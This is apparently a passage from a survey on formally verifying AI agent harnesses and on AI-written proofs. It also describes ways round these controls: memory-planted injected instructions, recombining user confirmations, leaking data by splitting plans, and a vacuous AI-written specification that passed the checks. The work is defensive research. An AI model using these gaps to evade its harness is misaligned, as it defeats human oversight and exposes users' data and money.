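Storing the full trace would take more and more memory. Programmers can instead store a smaller monitor state if they prove that it stays consistent with the trace. The web server stores which files the handler has opened, which connections have received data, and whether the current request has been answered.

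Let P be a verified program whose postcondition ψ describes the whole run, P↓ the same program with its checks added, and C any unverified code. F* has checked a proof of:

beh(C[P↓]) ⊆ ψ

C[P↓] denotes the two pieces of code linked together, and beh gives all the traces and results they can produce. For the web server, this means every request gets a response, whatever the handler does.

In an agent, the unverified program usually has control and calls the harness's operations. Andrici and colleagues prove a version of the theorem for this case too, but it guarantees only that the run obeys the policy. In one of their examples, a library refuses any operation unless a log entry for it comes directly before. Requiring an approved request instead of a log entry would give the maintenance agent's rule about writing.

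A stronger theorem compares attackers. For every C, there is some code C′ that respects the original interface, such that for every program P:

beh(C[P↓]) = beh(C′[P])

An attacker who ignores the interface therefore gains nothing over one who respects it. This also preserves properties that compare several runs, such as noninterference. A failed check returns an error that may reveal something about a secret, which is consistent with the theorem because C′ has access to the same checks.

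The solver did most of the server's verification, but the researchers had to state a few lemmas about traces and prove them by induction, which the solver could not do alone. F* automatically proved three of the four conditions for connecting the handler. The paper gives no figures for hours or lines of proof, so its evidence about the effort required is only qualitative.

The theorems apply to programs that terminate and to unverified code in a subset of F* or a small language that translates into it. They do not cover the code that runs. To try the server with a real browser, the researchers used F*'s standard translation to OCaml, which has no correctness proof.

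*Misquoted No More* (Andrici, Pribisova et al., 2026) closes part of this gap. It presents a translation from simple F* programs into a small typed language, with a proof in F* that the translation preserves the same strong security property. Its example is a wrapper around an unverified AI agent. The wrapper reads a file, lets the agent change it, then rereads it and reports success only if the new contents are a correct result for the task. The wrapper checks only that file, so on its own it would not detect changes to other files. The translation does not yet support general recursion. A related framework, *SecRef* (Andrici and Hriţcu, 2025), protects verified programs that share memory with unverified code.

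### Machine-checked proofs about agent software

*λ_A* (Liu, 2026) defines a small typed language for agent configurations, with 42 theorems in 1,519 lines of Coq. Liu proves, among other things, that a well-typed agent either returns a result of the right type or fails a declared check, and that loops with a step limit end. The types do not limit an agent's effects, because a tool that deletes a file and one that counts words can both have the type Str → Str, where Str is text. Liu leaves an effect system for later work. The proofs assume that every tool returns a result for every input and that every model call returns, so they do not cover tools that crash or hang.

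The paper's statement of one theorem is also too strong. It says that a loop with limit n runs its body at most n times, and the argument assumes that the body calls the loop again at most once. But the typing rules also allow a body that does so twice:

s ↦ (x ↦ s(s(x)))

If the body of a loop with limit n calls the loop twice, each time with the limit reduced by one, the body runs 2ⁿ − 1 times, or over a million times for a limit of 20. Such a loop still ends, and an ordinary agent loop calls itself only once. The Coq version presumably proves something narrower, such as a bound on how deeply the calls are nested, so anyone relying on the result would need to check the Coq statement. The difference matters because Liu derives a cost limit from the step count, for example $0.20 for 20 model calls at one cent each.

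PerMIT, by contrast, does restrict actions. Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026), in *PerMIT*, protect an agent's long-term memory, where a hostile instruction from a web page could lie unused until a later session. They used Lean to check two theorems for the single-user core:

- Every argument that reaches a sensitive tool is a value that the user typed exactly or confirmed exactly for that tool.
- If two runs have the same user inputs and random choices, and the user sees the same displays and makes the same decisions, the agent behaves the same way, however much the untrusted memory differs.

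A confirmation covers a value and a tool, but not the rest of the call. Suppose a user confirms $900 for a payment to a landlord and later confirms an unfamiliar account for a $5 payment. A call that sends $900 to the unfamiliar account satisfies the first theorem. The theorems also assume that whoever confirms a value means to authorise it. PerMIT allows a language model to do the confirming, and no proof covers that model's judgement. The Lean files are available only on request, so outsiders must request them before they can repeat the check.

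*Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) comes closer to a proof about running software. The system sends each tool call to a compiled Lean program, which decides whether to allow it before Python runs the tool. The functions that make these decisions are the same ones that appear in the proofs.

Many of the proofs concern changes to permissions that calls use up. Extending such a permission can block a legitimate task as well as allow a new action. Suppose an agent may delete file B once under its first permission and file A once under its second, so it can delete A and then B. A developer then extends the first permission to cover either file. The system uses the first permission that fits, so deleting A uses up the extended permission, and the agent can't then delete B. But it can delete A twice, which the old rules prevented.

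Agenra certifies a change if every call that the old permissions allowed remains possible under the new ones, at every point in a sequence of calls. The researchers wrote 51 changes to test this. Agenra certified all 21 that preserved the existing tasks and none of the 30 that broke one. A certified change can still be unsafe. For example, raising the number of times an agent may send a report from one to two preserves every task but lets it send a second copy.

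The proofs assume that calls happen one at a time and that outside services return the same results under both policies. Shivakumar and colleagues also trust the Python code that translates policies and carries requests to Lean, and trust each tool to perform only its declared effects. Their method of hiding values from the agent does not protect against arbitrary Python code in the same process.

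In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) verified a version of the loop that carries out an agent's actions in PocketFlow, a small Python framework. They wrote it in Dafny, a language whose verifier checks programs against stated conditions. They represented the AI as a function with no body that may return any value of the type Action, so the proof has to hold for every action the type allows. The policy allows the agent to read files only inside a workspace folder, call only listed tools, and take only a limited number of steps.

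The proof uses a simple state machine that describes safe behaviour and a more detailed one that describes the loop. It shows that the two start in matching states and that every step of the detailed machine matches a safe step of the simple one. By induction, every event in every run obeys the policy. Like the main theorem of *Alignment Contracts*, the proof requires no assumptions about the model.

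Dafny then translates the verified code into Python. The proof covers the state machine, and it extends to the running program only if Dafny's translator and the code that turns the model's text into an Action are correct, and if every outside effect appears as an event. Moon and Varshney tested the Python version with permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only the permitted ones. This proof provides part of the last of the five proofs that a verified harness needs.

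### Verifying a whole plan before it runs

In *Guardians of the Agents*, Meijer proposes checking an agent's entire plan before it runs. The model writes the plan as structured data, an analysis tool or solver checks it against a policy, and the harness runs it only if it passes. For example, a policy could forbid any data flow from fetched emails into the body of a message sent outside the company.

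Solvers can check stronger conditions, but people have to state them fully. Suppose a user asks an agent to delete foo.txt and bar.txt, and the model's plan deletes `*.txt`, meaning every text file. This plan satisfies the condition "foo.txt and bar.txt no longer exist". The specification also needs a frame condition, which says what must stay the same. If F is the set of files before the run and F′ the set afterwards, the full condition is:

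F′ = F \ {foo.txt, bar.txt}

The plan now fails if the folder could contain any other text file. Meijer's frame condition for the deletion tool requires that files not matching the given pattern remain. The plan as a whole also needs a frame condition, because deleting `*.txt` satisfies the tool's condition even if it removes other text files.

In a later talk, *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act*, Meijer (2026) suggests having the model supply a proof with its plan. After a step that reads a file, the rest of the plan is a function of the file's contents, so the proof must cover every text the file might contain. The harness checks the proof, and a trusted interpreter carries out the plan. *Return of the Theorem* (Meijer, 2026) instead describes automatic checks with solvers and formal business rules.

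Such a plan can contain branches, but the model has to write them before it sees the data. The maintenance agent would have to plan a repair to parser.py without having read it. It could leave the patch to a second model, as CaMeL does with untrusted text, but it could not change its approach if it found halfway through that the bug was in another file. Meijer believes that planning in code improves a model's reasoning, though he notes that nobody had formally measured the effect. One later result suggests that planning in advance can make an agent much less useful. According to Jiang and colleagues, CaMeL's configurations scored zero for usefulness on AgentDyn, a benchmark of tasks that require adapting along the way.

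The model could also write a new plan each time it receives new information, but checking each plan separately can miss a leak. In the email example, the first plan might fetch the messages and return a summary to the model. The second plan could then send that summary to an outsider as fixed text. Because the second plan never fetches any email, the checker finds no forbidden flow in it. To prevent this, the harness has to keep labels on data from one plan to the next, or hide the summary from the model, as TACIT does with its Classified wrapper.

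### Proofs written by AI

The labour of writing proofs has been the main obstacle to verifying software, and AI greatly reduced it in 2026. Earlier AI systems for Coq had proved between 12% and 48% of the theorems they attempted. In *Harnessing Code Agents for Automatic Software Verification*, Kan, Kan and Ertel (2026) gave Claude Code, running Claude Opus 4.7, one lemma at a time. It wrote a proof, received Coq's error messages and tried again, up to 30 times.

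Their system proved all 4,257 lemmas in the core of Iris, a framework for reasoning about programs whose parts run at the same time and share memory. It also proved all 217 lemmas about parts of Rust's standard library. One such lemma can take an expert hours or days to prove. The original proofs have been public for years, so many may have been in the model's training data. The system also proved 72 lemmas that nobody had yet ported to the unfinished Lean version of Iris, although it could have drawn on the Coq proofs for these too.

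According to Anthropic's *Safely scaling multi-agent teams with Claude Fable 5.2* (November 2026), dozens of agents working under one researcher wrote the first complete computer-checked proof of Fermat's Last Theorem in 11 days. Anthropic published the proof in September 2026. In the F* work on translating programs, Claude produced about 80 of the more than 900 definitions. Most were proofs of lemmas that Andrici and colleagues had already stated, and some were over 200 lines long. When the researchers later added refinement types, Claude updated existing proofs, so AI can also help keep proofs current as software changes.

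This should make several missing proofs practical. A Scala library that uses `@assumeSafe` needs the same kind of lemmas as those about Rust's library. AI could probably write most of the proof for the cached function described earlier, and much of a soundness proof for safe mode. But somebody first has to describe Scala's behaviour and the rules of safe mode in a proof assistant. If that description leaves out a language feature that bypasses the types, the proof can succeed even though code accepted by the real compiler can still bypass them.

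Stating the right theorem about an agent remains hard. The theorem has to include a policy and a description of files, processes and outside services, and a proof assistant cannot determine whether the policy matches what people want or whether the description matches how the computer behaves. By contrast, mathematicians agree on what Fermat's Last Theorem means: no positive whole numbers a, b and c satisfy aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ when n is a whole number greater than 2. Experts had also already written the statements of the Iris lemmas, and Kan and colleagues made their system reject any attempt that changed or dropped a lemma, assumed it as an axiom or left its proof unfinished.

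Moon and Varshney had Claude write specifications as well as proofs. In one of the two workflows they tested, the template for the safety rules had no field for the sensitive operation. When Claude could see the implementation, it left the nearest field empty, so the rule that every recorded item must obey the policy was true because there were no recorded items. Dafny still accepted the proof, and the specification passed all three of the researchers' automatic quality checks. When Claude could not see the implementation, it used the field to represent the operation, which gave the rule some content. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that each safety rule applies to something that can occur.

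If proofs took less effort to produce, they could also cover more of the trusted base, such as the Python layer in Agenra or the translator that Moon and Varshney rely on, but they cannot cover a remote service whose code is unavailable. Even with a verified compiler and verified libraries, the maintenance agent's harness could send its prompts to a model provider that stores them for longer than it promised.
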